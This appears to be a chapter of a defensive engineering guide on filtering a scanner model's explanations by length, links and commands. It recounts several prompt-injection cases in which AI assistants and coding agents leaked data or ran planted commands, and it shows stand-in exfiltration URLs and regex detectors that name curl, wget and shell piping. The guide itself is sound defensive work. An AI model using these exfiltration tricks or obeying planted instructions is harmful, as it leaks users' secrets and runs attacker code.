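Current models differ greatly in how well they follow a length limit in the prompt. Lafuente-Mercado and colleagues told every model to stay within 3,000 words. GPT-6 Astra complied in all 50 of its briefs. Claude Opus 5 exceeded the limit in 27 of 30, and Gemini 3.8 Flash exceeded it in all 30, averaging 5,239 words. General ability doesn't explain the difference, since Muse Spark 1.3 wrote the best briefs in the test but exceeded the limit in 23 of 30.

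*LIFEBench* (2025) tested 26 models on lengths from 16 to 8,192 words. Most followed short limits reasonably well but got sharply worse beyond a certain length. In *Can MLLMs Critique Like Humans?*, nine models each wrote 3,681 critiques of photographs, with instructions to use 50 to 150 words. GPT-5.5, Kimi-K2.6 and Gemma-4-31B complied every time, while three small models did so less than half the time. All the critiques that broke the limit were too long.

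Other parts of the prompt can affect whether a model keeps to the length range. When the researchers added a list of aspects to discuss, the share of critiques within the range fell from 87% to 34% for InternVL3-8B and from 98.5% to 85% for Qwen3.5-397B. A team that edits its prompt should therefore measure the lengths again.

Models can also exceed very tight character limits. *LLMs for Customized Marketing Content Generation and Evaluation at Scale* (2025) used Claude Haiku to write advertising headlines that had to be under 30 characters. Most were too long whatever the prompt, but adding a second model call to shorten them worked.

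None of these tests used a 600-character limit on security text, so each team has to measure its own rate. The photograph study suggests asking for less than the limit, because the models wrote close to the top of the range, averaging 112 to 151 words. For acme-db, the prompt could ask for at most 70 words, roughly 450 characters, while the code enforces the 600-character limit.

### Truncating, rejecting or asking again

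The simplest response to an overlong text is to cut it at the limit. Suppose the 940 characters about acme-db have this layout:

| Characters | Content |
|---|---|
| 1–230 | What SQL injection lets an attacker do |
| 231–370 | The claim that the finding is safe to ignore |
| 371–560 | The "required action" and its shell command |
| 561–640 | The link to the unknown domain |
| 641–940 | A warning that the project stays vulnerable until someone installs 2.3.4 |

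Truncating the explanation at 600 characters keeps the false reassurance and the command, cuts the link off after its first 40 characters, and removes the warning. An attacker who can influence the explanation could deliberately cause this by adding filler at the beginning.

Cutting text to a length limit can make even honest text dangerous. "This finding is safe to ignore only if no untrusted user can log in" becomes dangerous when the cut falls after "ignore". A web address ending in .com can lose its last letter and end in .co, where someone else may own the name. If the tool checks links before cutting the text, it approves the full address, but the reader gets the shortened one. Cutting only at the end of a sentence keeps the link and the condition intact, but it can still remove a warning in a later sentence.

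Rejecting the whole text avoids the problems of truncation, but the reader loses an explanation that may have been fine. Asking the model for a shorter version often recovers it, but the new text has to be cleaned and pass every check again. The shorter version can also leave out the warning, just as truncation can. For a security tool, the best choice is to reject the text, ask once for a shorter version, and show a fixed message built from the scanner's own data if that fails too. Truncation is acceptable only for a preview that opens into the full, checked explanation.

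### Choosing the limit

The length limit should be based on the lengths of explanations that people have judged good. A limit based on what the model writes when unrestricted would be much too high. In the photograph study, models with no length instruction averaged 240 to 381 words, while the human critics averaged 54.

1. Collect about 200 explanations covering the tool's main types of finding, and have reviewers keep only those that are correct and no longer than they need to be. Replace the rejected ones until 200 remain.
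2. Clean each one and count its code points.
3. Sort the lengths and find the value that 99% of them do not exceed.
4. Round it up a little and check that a text of that length fits the display.
5. Read every good explanation that the limit would refuse.

Suppose the 198th of the 200 lengths is 570, and the last two are 585 and 610. A limit of 600 would refuse one good explanation in 200. Because the sample is small, the true share of good explanations refused could be as high as about 1.5% even if the limit refused none of the 200, by the rule of thumb that divides three by the sample size.

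The last step matters because the longest good explanations may be about the most complicated and serious findings. If so, a single limit would reject the explanations readers need most, and the tool should set a higher limit for those types of finding. A separate limit for each language is also sensible because the same content can take far fewer characters in Chinese than in English.

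## Filtering links to untrusted domains

A link to an unknown domain, like the one in the acme-db explanation, can do two kinds of harm. The familiar one is phishing, where a reader who trusts the security tool follows the link to a page that imitates a login screen or offers a fake patch. The damage depends on what the page contains and whether the reader believes it.

A link can also leak private data. A browser sends the full address to the server it contacts, and servers usually log the addresses they receive. If an attacker gets the model to write private data into an address, as in `https://evil.example/log?data=...`, he can read it in his server's log even if the page is blank. A scanner's model may have seen source code, internal host names and a list of unfixed vulnerabilities, all of which would help an intruder.

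An ordinary link normally leaks data only when someone clicks it, but an image leaks it without a click, because the browser fetches the image as soon as it shows the text. The security company PromptArmor warns that chat apps with automatic link previews cause the same problem for ordinary links. Blocking images is therefore urgent but not enough. *Trust No AI* (2024), a catalogue of prompt-injection exploits, describes a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot that attackers could exploit with only a clickable link. A phishing email made Copilot search the user's inbox and put what it found into the link as invisible characters. Microsoft fixed the flaw in July 2024. Amazon dealt with a similar leak in its Amazon Q for Business assistant by no longer rendering links.

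### The Gemini Cloud Assist case

Gemini Cloud Assist, Google's assistant for its cloud customers, can explain log entries. Tenable's *The Trifecta* describes how the company's researchers turned that feature into a phishing tool.

The researchers set up a mock victim with a Cloud Function, a small program that runs when it receives a web request. They sent it a request with instructions for Gemini in the User-Agent header, which Google's logging service stored with the rest of the request. Because the log entry was structured data, the researchers began their text with the characters that close a field, so that Gemini would read the rest as if it were outside the log entry.

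When the victim pressed the "Explain this log entry" button, Gemini repeated the attacker's message in its summary, including a phishing link. Asking an ordinary question, such as what the latest function run was, could have had the same effect because Gemini would look up the logs to answer it. The screen shortened the prompt details, so the victim could see the injected text only by opening "Additional prompt details".

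The attacker needed no account. Tenable notes that an attacker could have sent the same request to every public-facing service on Google's cloud and waited for someone to ask Gemini about the logs. Tenable says it "should be possible" to extract data too, using planted text that tells Gemini to look up security misconfigurations and put them into a link. It demonstrated only the phishing link.

Tenable reported the problem on 19 December 2024, and Google said on 5 March 2025 that it was fixed. Google stopped rendering links in all log summaries. The reader now sees the raw Markdown, with the address written out after the word, instead of a clickable word.

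Replacing a link with its plain-text address means readers can't click it and can see where it leads. Little is lost, because a log summary rarely needs a link. But a reader can still copy the address into a browser, and a ticket system that renders Markdown can make it clickable again. A tool that can reject the whole explanation should do that instead.

### Finding every link

A filter can only check the links it detects, and Markdown has many ways to write one. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reconstructs an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that exploited this, which the security firm Aim Labs found in January 2025. The attacker sends an employee of the target company an email that reads like a business request but contains instructions for Copilot. When the employee later asks Copilot about something confidential, Copilot retrieves the email along with the company's own files and puts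 sensitive details into a URL in its answer.

A Microsoft filter removed inline links but missed reference-style links, in which the sentence contains only a label and the address is on a separate line. An attack used reference-style links, and with a reference-style image the user didn't have to click. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its servers in May 2025 and said it had no evidence of real attacks.

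Attackers can also try several forms at once. In an attack on Google's coding tool Antigravity that 0DIN, Mozilla's bug-bounty program for AI, describes, the planted text asks the model to write one image in five formats. The attack succeeds if the display loads any of them. A link check therefore has to cover at least these forms:

| Form | Example | Why it matters |
|---|---|---|
| Inline link | `[advisory](https://evil.example/a)` | Most filters look for this one |
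| Reference-style link | `[advisory][1]`, with `[1]: https://evil.example/a` on another line | Copilot's filter missed it |
| Automatic link | `<https://evil.example/a>` | A filter may mistake it for an HTML tag |
| Bare address | `https://evil.example/a` or `www.evil.example` | Many chat and ticket systems make it clickable |
| HTML link | `<a href="https://evil.example/a">` | Many Markdown viewers accept HTML |
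| Image | `![chart](https://evil.example/a)` or an HTML image tag | Loads without a click |
| Non-web scheme | Addresses that begin with `javascript:`, `data:`, `file:` or `mailto:` | Can run script, open a local file or start an email |

The procedure runs on the cleaned text, so invisible characters cannot break up an address.

1. Parse the text with the same Markdown parser, and the same settings, as the display. Collect the address from every link, image and HTML tag.
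2. Search the remaining text for bare addresses.
3. Refuse the text if any address has a scheme other than `https`.
4. Parse each address, normalize its host and compare it with the tool's rule.
5. Take out the accepted links and refuse the text if anything that looks like an address is left.

If a team writes its own pattern for Markdown links instead of using the display's parser, the pattern will treat some text differently from the display, and an attacker can exploit any difference. The last step is necessary even with the right parser, because many parsers drop a reference address that no label uses. The address is then missing from the collected links but remains in the stored text, where another program may find it.

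Security explanations often mention file names, which can be hard to tell apart from bare web addresses. The endings `.py`, `.rs`, `.md` and `.sh` are also the country domains of Paraguay, Serbia, Moldova and Saint Helena, so a ticket system may turn `setup.py` or `README.md` into a link. A dependency scanner can accept a file name that exactly matches the finding's location and treat other names with a real domain ending as addresses. A log viewer should not make this exception, because an outsider may have chosen the file name in the request.

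### Reading the host correctly

In the address `https://advisories.example/acme-db?id=7`, `https` is the scheme, `advisories.example` is the host, `/acme-db` is the path and `id=7` is the query. The host determines which server the browser contacts. Suppose the tool trusts `advisories.example`. Several obvious tests for that host fail:

| Test | Address that passes | Host the browser contacts |
|---|---|---|
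| The address contains `advisories.example` | `https://evil.example/advisories.example` | `evil.example` |
| The address starts with `https://advisories.example` | `https://advisories.example.evil.example/` | `advisories.example.evil.example` |
| The address starts with `https://advisories.example` | `https://advisories.example@evil.example/` | `evil.example` |
| The host ends with `advisories.example` | `https://notadvisories.example/` | `notadvisories.example` |

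In a link, everything between the two slashes and an @ sign is a username, which the browser doesn't use to find the server. An attacker can put a trusted domain there and their own host after the @ sign.

The "ends with" test wrongly accepts `notadvisories.example` because it compares characters rather than *labels*, the parts of a domain name separated by dots. Anyone can register that name without involving the owner of `advisories.example`. Code that compares whole labels from the right rejects it, because `notadvisories` and `advisories` differ, but accepts `www.advisories.example`, whose last two labels match.

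Even a proper parser can pick the wrong host, because parsers disagree about malformed addresses. Python's standard library reads the host of `https://evil.example\@advisories.example/` as `advisories.example`. Browsers treat the backslash as a slash and go to `evil.example`. It is safer to refuse unusual addresses before parsing them:

```python
import re
from urllib.parse import urlsplit

TRUSTED_HOSTS = {"advisories.example", "docs.scanner.example"}
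PLAIN_URL = re.compile(r"https://[A-Za-z0-9.-]+(/[A-Za-z0-9._~/-]*)?")

def host_allowed(url):
    if not PLAIN_URL.fullmatch(url):
        return False
    host = urlsplit(url).hostname.removesuffix(".")
    return host in TRUSTED_HOSTS

def under_domain(host, domain):          # only if subdomains are acceptable
    labels, wanted = host.split("."), domain.split(".")
    return labels[-len(wanted):] == wanted
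```

The pattern rejects @ signs, backslashes, port numbers, percent codes and queries. Normalization lowercases the host, which `urlsplit` does, and removes a final dot, which is legal and doesn't change the destination. Look-alike names need no special treatment here, though a list of forbidden domains would have to anticipate all of them. A host with a Cyrillic letter fails the pattern, and its ASCII form, which begins with `xn--`, is not in the set of allowed domains.

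`host_allowed` accepts only exact hosts. A team should use `under_domain` only if the domain's owner controls every subdomain, which isn't the case for hosting services that give each customer a subdomain. Even a careful owner can forget an old subdomain that points to a service they no longer use, and an attacker may be able to take over that subdomain.

### Four rules for accepting an address

The function above applies a *domain allowlist*, which compares the host with a fixed list. The check takes little compute and no network access, and anyone can audit the list by reading it. The main drawback is that someone has to keep the list up to date. Simon Willison, a programmer who collects data-leak cases on his weblog, describes a 2025 failure at Salesforce. Its AI agents ran in a page with a *content security policy*, a list of the hosts from which the browser may load the page's resources.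 The policy still included a domain that had expired. Researchers registered the domain and showed that the agent would send customers' sales leads to it.

An allowlist can also be too strict. OpenAI argues in *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) that people visit far more sites than any list can hold, and that frequent warnings may train them to click through without thinking. This is a serious objection for a general assistant, but a dependency scanner whose legitimate links lead to three or four hosts would seldom block a useful link.

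The list of allowed links can also come from the documents given to the model instead of a fixed setting. Yelp's *The Evolution of Support* (May 2026) reports that the company built its support chatbot this way because models often invented links. For each question, the software retrieves at most five of about 370 help articles and gives them to the model. Before the answer is sent, code checks that every link in it comes from one of those articles. Yelp gives no figures for how often this check finds an invented link.

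Yelp's method works because Yelp controls the articles. A security tool's sources include package descriptions and log fields, so an attacker who writes an address into one of them gets it onto the list. The comparison must also use whole addresses. *Environment Steering* (2026), which proposes rules for what AI agents may do with data, includes an example that uses a `contains` test to check whether a value appears in a page's text. For links, such a test would accept `https://advisories.example/12` when the source mentions only `https://advisories.example/123`, or a host ending in `.co` when the source has the same host ending in `.com`.

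OpenAI uses a third rule for addresses that ChatGPT loads automatically. Its web crawler, which has no access to conversations or accounts, records the addresses it finds on the public web. ChatGPT may load an address without asking only if the crawler has already recorded that exact address. OpenAI reasons that an address that existed before the conversation is unlikely to contain data from it. For any other address, ChatGPT has to look for another site or warn the user that the link is unverified and may include information from the conversation.

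This rule is meant to prevent leaks, and OpenAI says it does not guarantee that a page is trustworthy. A phishing site passes if the crawler has visited it. The rule also needs an index of the web, which few makers of security tools have. It works badly for links to a company's internal pages and to an advisory published an hour ago, which may be the link an analyst most needs.

The fourth rule is a *provenance check*, which accepts a link only if that exact address came from a trusted source rather than from the model. Anthropic applies a version of this to Claude's tool for opening web pages. According to Willison, Claude may open only addresses that the user typed or a search returned, and code outside the model enforces this. An instruction to add the user's answers to an address and open the result therefore fails.

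How well this works depends on which sources count as trusted. When Anthropic released the tool to developers in September 2025, it accepted any address from a user message. Willison pointed out that many applications paste untrusted content into those messages. *Environment Steering* adds a second model that judges whether an attacker planted the value in the page, but an attacker may fool that model too. A security tool needs less guesswork because its designer knows which fields outsiders can write, and can label each input field as trusted or untrusted. Code then collects addresses only from the trusted fields. The labels have to be right, and someone has to review them whenever the tool gains a new input.

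Google combines several methods in Gemini. It says that its Markdown sanitizer doesn't render external images, and that Gemini checks for suspicious addresses with Safe Browsing, Google's service for identifying dangerous sites. Google's newer *How Gemini’s defense-in-depth approach works* also describes fixed rules outside the model that restrict which addresses Gemini can open or send information to. Google says it uses these rules because "no detector catches every injection attempt". The account doesn't specify the criteria for these restrictions, so outsiders can't tell how much they depend on where an address came from.

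### How link filters have failed

Redirects have defeated filters that look only at the host in a link. Many trusted sites run pages that send the browser to another address. An earlier ChatGPT check, url_safe, decided which links and images were safe to show. Tenable found that Bing serves its search results through bing.com addresses that redirect to the listed sites. These addresses passed the check, so an attacker could use one to send users to their own site.

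The last step of EchoLeak similarly sent stolen data through a permitted host. Copilot's content security policy stopped the browser from loading images from unknown hosts, but it permitted a Microsoft Teams host with a preview service that fetched any address it received. The browser sent the service an attacker's address containing the stolen data, and the service fetched it. The policy did not block this because the browser itself contacted only the permitted host.

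If the checker followed each link to see where it ends, the request would itself deliver any data in the address, and the attacker's server could send the checker somewhere harmless and the reader somewhere else. It is better to keep hosts with open redirects off the list and to refuse links with queries, since redirect pages usually expect the destination there. The pattern in `host_allowed` refuses queries, but a few services put the destination in the path, so the hosts on the list must still be chosen carefully.

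Attackers can steal data without a redirect if a permitted site stores what strangers send it. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes such an attack on an email application with a built-in assistant. Superhuman's policy permitted docs.google.com, which also hosts Google Forms, and a form can accept an answer submitted through its URL. PromptArmor put instructions in an email. When the user asked for a summary of recent mail, the assistant wrote an image whose URL submitted the contents of other emails to PromptArmor's form. The browser sent them when it tried to load the image. One answer contained parts of more than 40 emails, and the user never had to open the malicious one. PromptArmor reported this on the night of Friday, 5 December 2025, and Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features the following Monday.

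Willison records two more cases in which an allowed domain could leak data. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, could reach Anthropic's API, so an attacker could supply their own API key and have the agent upload files to the attacker's account. The default allowlist in Google's Antigravity included webhook.site, a service for recording incoming requests. Anyone writing an allowlist should therefore check whether outsiders can read what each host receives.

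A host can be used for phishing if strangers can publish on it. Code-hosting sites allow this, but they also host many genuine advisories. The tool can permit only the part of the site that holds the advisories, provided it rejects paths containing `..`. Browsers treat `..` as the parent folder, so a link could otherwise lead outside the permitted part.

The Google Forms leak also shows that a company can have a defense and not use it everywhere. OpenAI published its index rule in January 2026. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* reports that in April the same trick worked in Codex, OpenAI's agent for coding and office tasks. An index built from public pages could not have contained an address with the victim's emails in it, so Codex was probably not applying the rule to images. OpenAI has since fixed the flaw. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations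 in New Paper* lists such gaps as a remaining risk, because not every developer in a large company knows that a mitigation exists.

OpenAI acknowledges in its paper that even an index rule applied everywhere still lets data leak, though more slowly. An attacker needs 36 ordinary public pages, one for each letter and digit. If the attacker can get an agent to visit them in the right order, the visits spell out a secret, although every address existed beforehand. With 4,096 pages, each visit conveys 12 bits, a little more than two characters. Embrace The Red suggests that agents should not load the same address twice in a session. This makes the attack harder, but an attacker can avoid repeat visits by preparing a separate page for each character in each position.

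Claude's provenance rule had a similar flaw, which Ayush Paul demonstrated in July 2026. The tool accepted links that appeared in pages it had already fetched. Paul built a site that told AI assistants to identify their user by browsing profiles letter by letter, and his server generated the next set of links at each step. Claude revealed the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic fixed the flaw by stopping the tool from following links in fetched pages.

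The slow leak is much smaller for a tool that only displays text. If the tool limits each explanation to one link, which the model chooses from 50 known addresses, a click reveals at most about 5.6 bits, enough to answer five yes-or-no questions.

### Prompt rules and network rules

Some developers put the link rule in the prompt and tell the model never to follow instructions in outside data. Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, tested how much this helps. Their agent, built on the small model Qwen2.5-7B, summarized web pages and could make web requests. In 480 runs, the pages contained an instruction to send a secret from the agent's context to the attacker's server, and the agent sent it in 423 of them (88%). It sent the secret in none of the 120 runs with harmless pages.

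In 95% of the successful attacks, the agent's final answer looked harmless. Checking that answer would have missed nearly all of these leaks, because the agent had already made the request itself. An output filter covers only the links that a reader or a later program might open. If the model that writes explanations can also load web pages, the same allowlist has to apply to its requests.

The team then compared defenses on one of the most successful forms of the attack, with 30 runs for each.

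| Defense | Runs in which data left |
|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| Prompt says web content is data, not commands | 67% |
| Tags around outside content, marked as untrusted | 100% |
| Prompt rule and tags together | 57% |
| Domain allowlist on requests | 0% |
| "Redirect detection" | 0% |
| Filter for words such as `password` in the address | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking values in the address | 0% |

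The allowlist result would hold for any model, because code blocks the request whatever the model writes. The test was easy, though, because Lan and colleagues chose an attacker domain that no sensible list would include. They point out that compromised sites, subdomain takeovers and open redirects could get around a list in practice.

The other zeros are weaker evidence. Despite its name, the "redirect detection" filter doesn't follow redirects. It blocks numeric addresses, certain domain endings and paths that contain words such as `steal` or `collect`. The attacker's domain ended in `.net`, which the filter doesn't block, but the attack address printed in the paper contains `/collect`. That word probably triggered the block, and an attacker could choose another. With the filter for random-looking values, the agent made no attempts at all. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoided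 such values while the filter was active, but a filter that runs after the model has written the address shouldn't change what the model writes, so this result is hard to interpret.

The prompt results come from a small model with a minimal system prompt and the secret placed directly in its context. Current models probably resist simple instructions better, but even a small failure rate helps an attacker who can keep trying.

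### Applying the rules to acme-db

If the acme-db explanation links to `https://acme-db-patches.example/fix`, the model might have invented the address, or the package's publisher might have put it in the package description. The last column covers the case where the model invents a page on a host the tool trusts, such as `https://advisories.example/acme-db-fix`.

| Rule | The model invented the address | It was in the package description | Invented page on a trusted host |
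|---|---|---|---|
| Domain allowlist | Refuses | Refuses | Accepts |
| Allowlist from the model's sources | Refuses | Accepts, if the description counts as a source | Refuses |
| Public index | Refuses, unless such a page exists and is indexed | Accepts once the crawler has seen the page | Refuses, unless such a page exists and is indexed |
| Provenance check | Refuses | Refuses, if the description is labelled untrusted | Refuses |

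An invented domain can be dangerous even if it doesn't exist yet. If models tend to invent the same plausible domain, an attacker can register it and wait for visitors. An invented page on a trusted host is usually only a dead link, but its path can carry data to a host that outsiders may be able to read.

For a tool like this one, the best default is to allow no addresses in the model's text, even to trusted domains, because code already copies the advisory link into a separate field. This is stricter than any of the four rules and easier to build.

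This also makes detection simpler. Every form in the earlier table contains either a scheme or a domain name, so code can search the raw text for those and doesn't have to imitate anyone's Markdown parser:

```python
SCHEME = re.compile(r"\b(?:https?|ftp|file|data|javascript|mailto):\S|//\w", re.I)
DOTTED = re.compile(r"[a-z0-9_-]+(?:\.[a-z0-9_-]+)+", re.I)
# TOP_LEVEL: the official list of domain endings (com, org, io, py ...), in lower case

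def has_address(text, known_files=()):
    if SCHEME.search(text):
        return True
    return any(word not in known_files and word.lower().rsplit(".", 1)[-1] in TOP_LEVEL
               for word in DOTTED.findall(text))
```

The function accepts the version number `2.3.4` and `java.sql.Statement` because neither `4` nor `Statement` is a domain ending. For a finding in `setup.py`, the caller passes that file name in `known_files`. The function sometimes causes a *false block*, meaning it refuses harmless text. For example, it refuses a sentence about code that contains `user.name`, because `.name` is a real domain ending. It also refuses text with a missing space after a full stop if the next word is a domain ending, such as "to" or "it". A team can reduce these cases by telling the model in the prompt not to write addresses, and by asking once for a new version if it does, as with overlong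 text.

The copied advisory link also needs to be checked. Public vulnerability records include reference links from many contributors, so a trusted database can contain untrusted addresses. Code should run the link through `host_allowed` and omit it if the check fails. If the advisory site uses predictable addresses, code can instead build the link from the finding's identifier, after checking that the identifier has the expected format. The interface should show the full address next to the link so that readers can see where it leads.

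If the explanation needs to link to more than one page, the model can choose from a fixed set such as "advisory", "release notes" and "upgrade guide", and code supplies the address for each. A tool that draws on hundreds of documents, like Yelp's chatbot, can't list its links this way. It should accept only complete addresses that appear in documents its owner controls, and also check their hosts against a fixed list.

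## Detecting commands presented as required actions

A reader who opens a HIGH finding expects to have to act on it. A supplied command looks like the fastest way to do that, and the reader has little reason to doubt it because it appears in a security tool. The command runs with the reader's permissions, which on a developer's machine often cover source code and cloud accounts. In the acme-db explanation, the words "required action" add pressure to run it. A coding agent that reads the explanation may run the command before a person sees it.

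### Cases from 2025 and 2026

In a *ClickFix* attack, a web page or email gives instructions for a supposed repair, such as pasting in a command, and victims infect their own computers by following them. In August 2025 the security company CloudSEK showed that an AI summary can pass on such instructions. Its test page had harmless visible text, dozens of hidden copies of the ClickFix steps, and a hidden prompt to output only those steps. Sider.ai's summary of the page included instructions to open the Windows Run dialog and paste in an encoded PowerShell command, which was harmless in this test.

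CloudSEK says the attack worked in most of its tests but gives no count, and it tried only a few summarizers. The attack depends on the summarizer reading raw HTML, so a tool that passes only the visible text to the model would avoid it. This doesn't help with logs, where planted instructions can be ordinary visible text.

A false warning can do harm without any command. *Phishing For Gemini* (Figueroa, 2025) describes an email with an instruction in white, zero-size text. When the recipient pressed "Summarize this email", Gemini added a warning to the summary that their Gmail password had been compromised and gave a phone number to call. The email had no link or attachment, and a filter that looks only for commands would have let the summary through.

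The 2026 cases involve coding agents. Tenet Security, an Israeli startup (not Tenable), attacked users of Sentry, which collects error reports from running applications. Anyone can send Sentry a report using a key that is public in websites' code. Tenet sent a fake error with a "Resolution" section containing a command. When a developer asked a coding agent to fix the unresolved errors, the agent read the report and ran the command. The Next Web's *Agentjacking* reports that this worked in 85% of controlled tests against Claude Code, Cursor and Codex, and that agents ran the code even when told to ignore untrusted data. Infosecurity Magazine's *New “Agentjacking” Attacks Could Hijack AI Coding Agents* reports that the planted text was indistinguishable from Sentry's own repair advice. Sentry called the problem "technically not defensible" and added a filter for one specific string, which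 an attacker can change to avoid the filter.

Tenet showed further attacks at the DEF CON security conference in August. SecurityWeek's *‘Ghostjacking’ Attack Uses Poisoned Logs to Turn AI Agents Bad* describes how a fake "urgent diagnostic" alert in the monitoring service Datadog led Claude Code to run the attacker's command and leak cloud credentials. Another attack used Seer, Sentry's own AI agent. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *“Ghostjacking” Exploits AI Agents’ Trusted Access to Evade Firewall Controls*, Seer read a fake report and presented the planted fix as its own conclusion, and a coding agent that trusted Seer then ran it. Output validation fits this case best, because the command was in Seer's output before it reached the agent that ran it.

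Academic tests have found lower rates. *Beyond the Payload* (2026) planted attacks in the files of code repositories and asked agents to do routine jobs. When the request was simply to run the project's tests, the attack succeeded in 45.0% of runs against Codex with GPT-5.5, which alerted the user in 2.5%. It succeeded in 12.5% of runs against Claude Code with Sonnet 4.6, which alerted the user in 7.5%. Tenet sells protection against such attacks and chose its own demonstrations, so its 85% is probably near the top of the range.

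### Two questions about the text

The command check tests whether the cleaned text contains anything executable and whether it presents an action as required.

```python
import re

INSTALL = (r"\b(?:npm|pnpm|yarn|pip3?|uv|gem|cargo|brew|apt(?:-get)?)\s+"
           r"(?:-\S+\s+)*(?:install|i|add|exec|run|upgrade)\b")
PROGRAM = (r"\b(?:curl|wget|bash|sh|cmd|powershell|pwsh|python3?|node)(?:\.exe)?\s+"
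           r"(?:-\w|\S*[/\\]|\S+\.(?:py|js|sh|ps1)\b)")
RUNNER  = r"\b(?:npx|uvx|sudo)\s+\S"
SHELL   = r"`{3}|&&|\|\||\$\(|\|\s*(?:ba|z)?sh\b"     # code blocks, shell syntax, piping into a shell
ENCODED = r"[A-Za-z0-9+/]{40,}"                       # long encoded text

EXECUTABLE = re.compile("|".join([INSTALL, PROGRAM, RUNNER, SHELL, ENCODED]), re.I)
OBLIGATION = re.compile(r"\b(?:must|required|mandatory|immediately|urgent(?:ly)?|"
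                        r"right away|before continuing)\b", re.I)
```

Program names alone are a poor test because many of them are also ordinary words or topics. A dependency scanner's output often mentions npm, so the pattern requires a subcommand after `npm` and an option or a file after `python`. Some harmless text still matches, such as the phrase "npm install scripts", a Java condition that uses `&&`, and a 40-character commit identifier.

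One rule can also catch a command that another misses. The encoded part of CloudSEK's test command was only eight characters long, so the rule for long encoded text would miss it, but the `PROGRAM` rule catches the PowerShell call around it.

The obligation pattern produces more false matches. An accurate explanation of acme-db could say that "the attacker must have an ordinary account" or that "no special privileges are required". Both phrases match, although they describe conditions for the attack rather than anything the reader must do. A match alone should therefore never be enough to refuse a text.

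An instruction can also be polite. Kao, Li and colleagues (2026), in *You Told Me to Do It*, planted instructions in README files, the introductory documents of software projects, to make agents leak private files. They phrased the instructions as direct orders and company policy, but also as friendly suggestions and requests to help the team. Some contained no shell command and only asked the agent to upload a file or email it to a colleague. Neither pattern would detect a polite request of that kind, though an agent with email access could carry it out.

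### Four combinations

The right response depends on both answers. The third column assumes that the tool builds the upgrade command itself, as described below.

| Text | Example | Response |
|---|---|---|
| No command, no obligation | "Any logged-in user could read the whole database." | Pass it on to the other checks |
| No command, obligation | "You must call this number immediately." | Find out what the text asks for; accept only upgrading or reviewing the affected code |
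| Command, no obligation | "You can fix this with `npm install acme-db@2.3.4`." | Refuse it and ask once for a version without commands |
| Command and obligation | "Required action: run this script before continuing." | Refuse it, don't ask again, and record it for a person to review |

In the second row, a pattern can't distinguish "you must upgrade" from "you must call this number". Figueroa recommends flagging or suppressing summaries that contain phone numbers, web addresses or urgent security language. A security tool that blocked all urgent language would refuse many honest texts, since some flaws are urgent. A better approach is to have a second model classify the requested action using a closed set of labels, such as "upgrade", "review code", "none" or "other", and to refuse any text labelled "other".

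A model may write "you must run" in honest advice, so the fourth row does not prove an attack. But if the input contains a planted instruction, a second request sends it to the model again and gives the attacker another chance.

A command can be unsafe even when it isn't presented as required. *Do Coding Agents Follow AGENTS.md?* (2026) tested how the wording of written project rules affects agents. Claude Code with Claude Opus 5 complied with 78.0% of direct instructions and 64.2% of conditional ones. Adding a reason to a direct instruction made no significant difference. Because an agent may also follow the weaker instructions, the tool refuses commands whether or not they are presented as required. The obligation wording affects only how it handles the refusal.

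### Pattern lists, parsers and classifier models

The usual remedy for a flawed dependency is a command, so a tool that refuses every command also blocks legitimate fixes. If the tool lets the model write commands, it has to tell good ones from bad ones. Kao and colleagues ran into the same difficulty with README files, which are full of legitimate installation commands. None of the 12 rule-based and 6 model-based defenses they tested was reliable without too many false alarms, and none of the 15 people in their user study noticed the planted instructions.

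The simplest method is to check the command against a list of dangerous patterns. A shell parser breaks the command into programs, arguments, pipes and redirections, so that a rule can refer to the program that writes to a protected file, however the command is written. A classifier model predicts whether the command is dangerous.

In *CARE*, Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) compared these methods on 220 dangerous and 329 harmless shell commands. Their own system, CARE, first undoes common disguises such as encoding and then parses the command. It scores the command by what the program does, which files it touches, which known attack patterns it matches and how it is structured. It allows low-scoring commands, refuses high-scoring ones and, in the full version, has a model judge most of the unclear cases.

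| Method | Dangerous commands caught | Harmless commands blocked | Average time |
|---|---|---|---|
| List of 22 patterns | 17% | 0% | 0.01 ms |
| CARE without a model | 76% | 1.8% | 0.34 ms |
| CARE with a model for unclear cases | 76% | 0.9% | 2.3 ms |
| Model alone (Qwen3-Coder-30B) | 67% | 11% | 46 ms |
| Safety classifier (Granite Guardian 2B) | 82% | 46% | 17 ms |

The parser contributes little to CARE's result. CARE still caught 73% of the dangerous commands without it, but only 42% without the rules about what each program does and 53% without the rules about file paths. A team that adds a parser but writes few rules is therefore unlikely to match CARE's result.

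The ranking also depends on the attacks. The 22 patterns scored higher than CARE on exploit code from the public archive Exploit-DB, with an F1 score (the harmonic mean of precision and recall) of 81.5 against 66.3. These exploits often contain standard destructive commands that simple patterns match.

A shell parser can't find the commands in an explanation, because shell grammar accepts most plain English. It parses "Upgrade the package today" as a program called `Upgrade` with three arguments. The tool has to locate likely commands, for example with the patterns above, before the parser examines them.

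Even a perfect check of shell commands would miss the kind of attack Tenet used. According to Hackread's *Agentjacking*, the planted command downloaded and ran a package from the public npm registry. Developers run commands like this every day, and the harm depends on which package they name. CARE's input includes the command and the file system but not the finding, so it can't check whether a package is relevant to the problem.

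Liu, Ma and Vorobeychik (2026), in *Robust Context-Aware Detection of Malicious Instructions in Text*, try to supply that context. They compute an embedding, a list of numbers representing the user's request and the whole document, then remove one sentence and compute it again. The difference between the two embeddings shows what the sentence adds to this document for this request. A small classifier uses that difference and the sentence's own embedding to classify the sentence as malicious or not. Training on more paraphrased attacks makes the classifier harder to fool but causes agents to complete fewer legitimate tasks. The method filters what an agent reads, but designers could try it on explanations by putting the finding in place of the user's request. They would have to retrain the classifier on security text, because the trade-off between resisting attacks and completing tasks varied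 considerably between subject areas.

Ready-made prompt-injection detectors need testing on a security tool's own text before anyone relies on them. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (2026) reports tests of these detectors on harmless output from agents' tools. ProtectAI v2 flagged 0.5% of ordinary web pages and 1.2% of emails, but 30.1% of the tool outputs in one benchmark and 66.9% in another. Horizon-Labs flagged 0.0% and 0.7% on the same two benchmarks. A low false-alarm rate doesn't show that a detector works, because a detector that never flags anything has a rate of zero.

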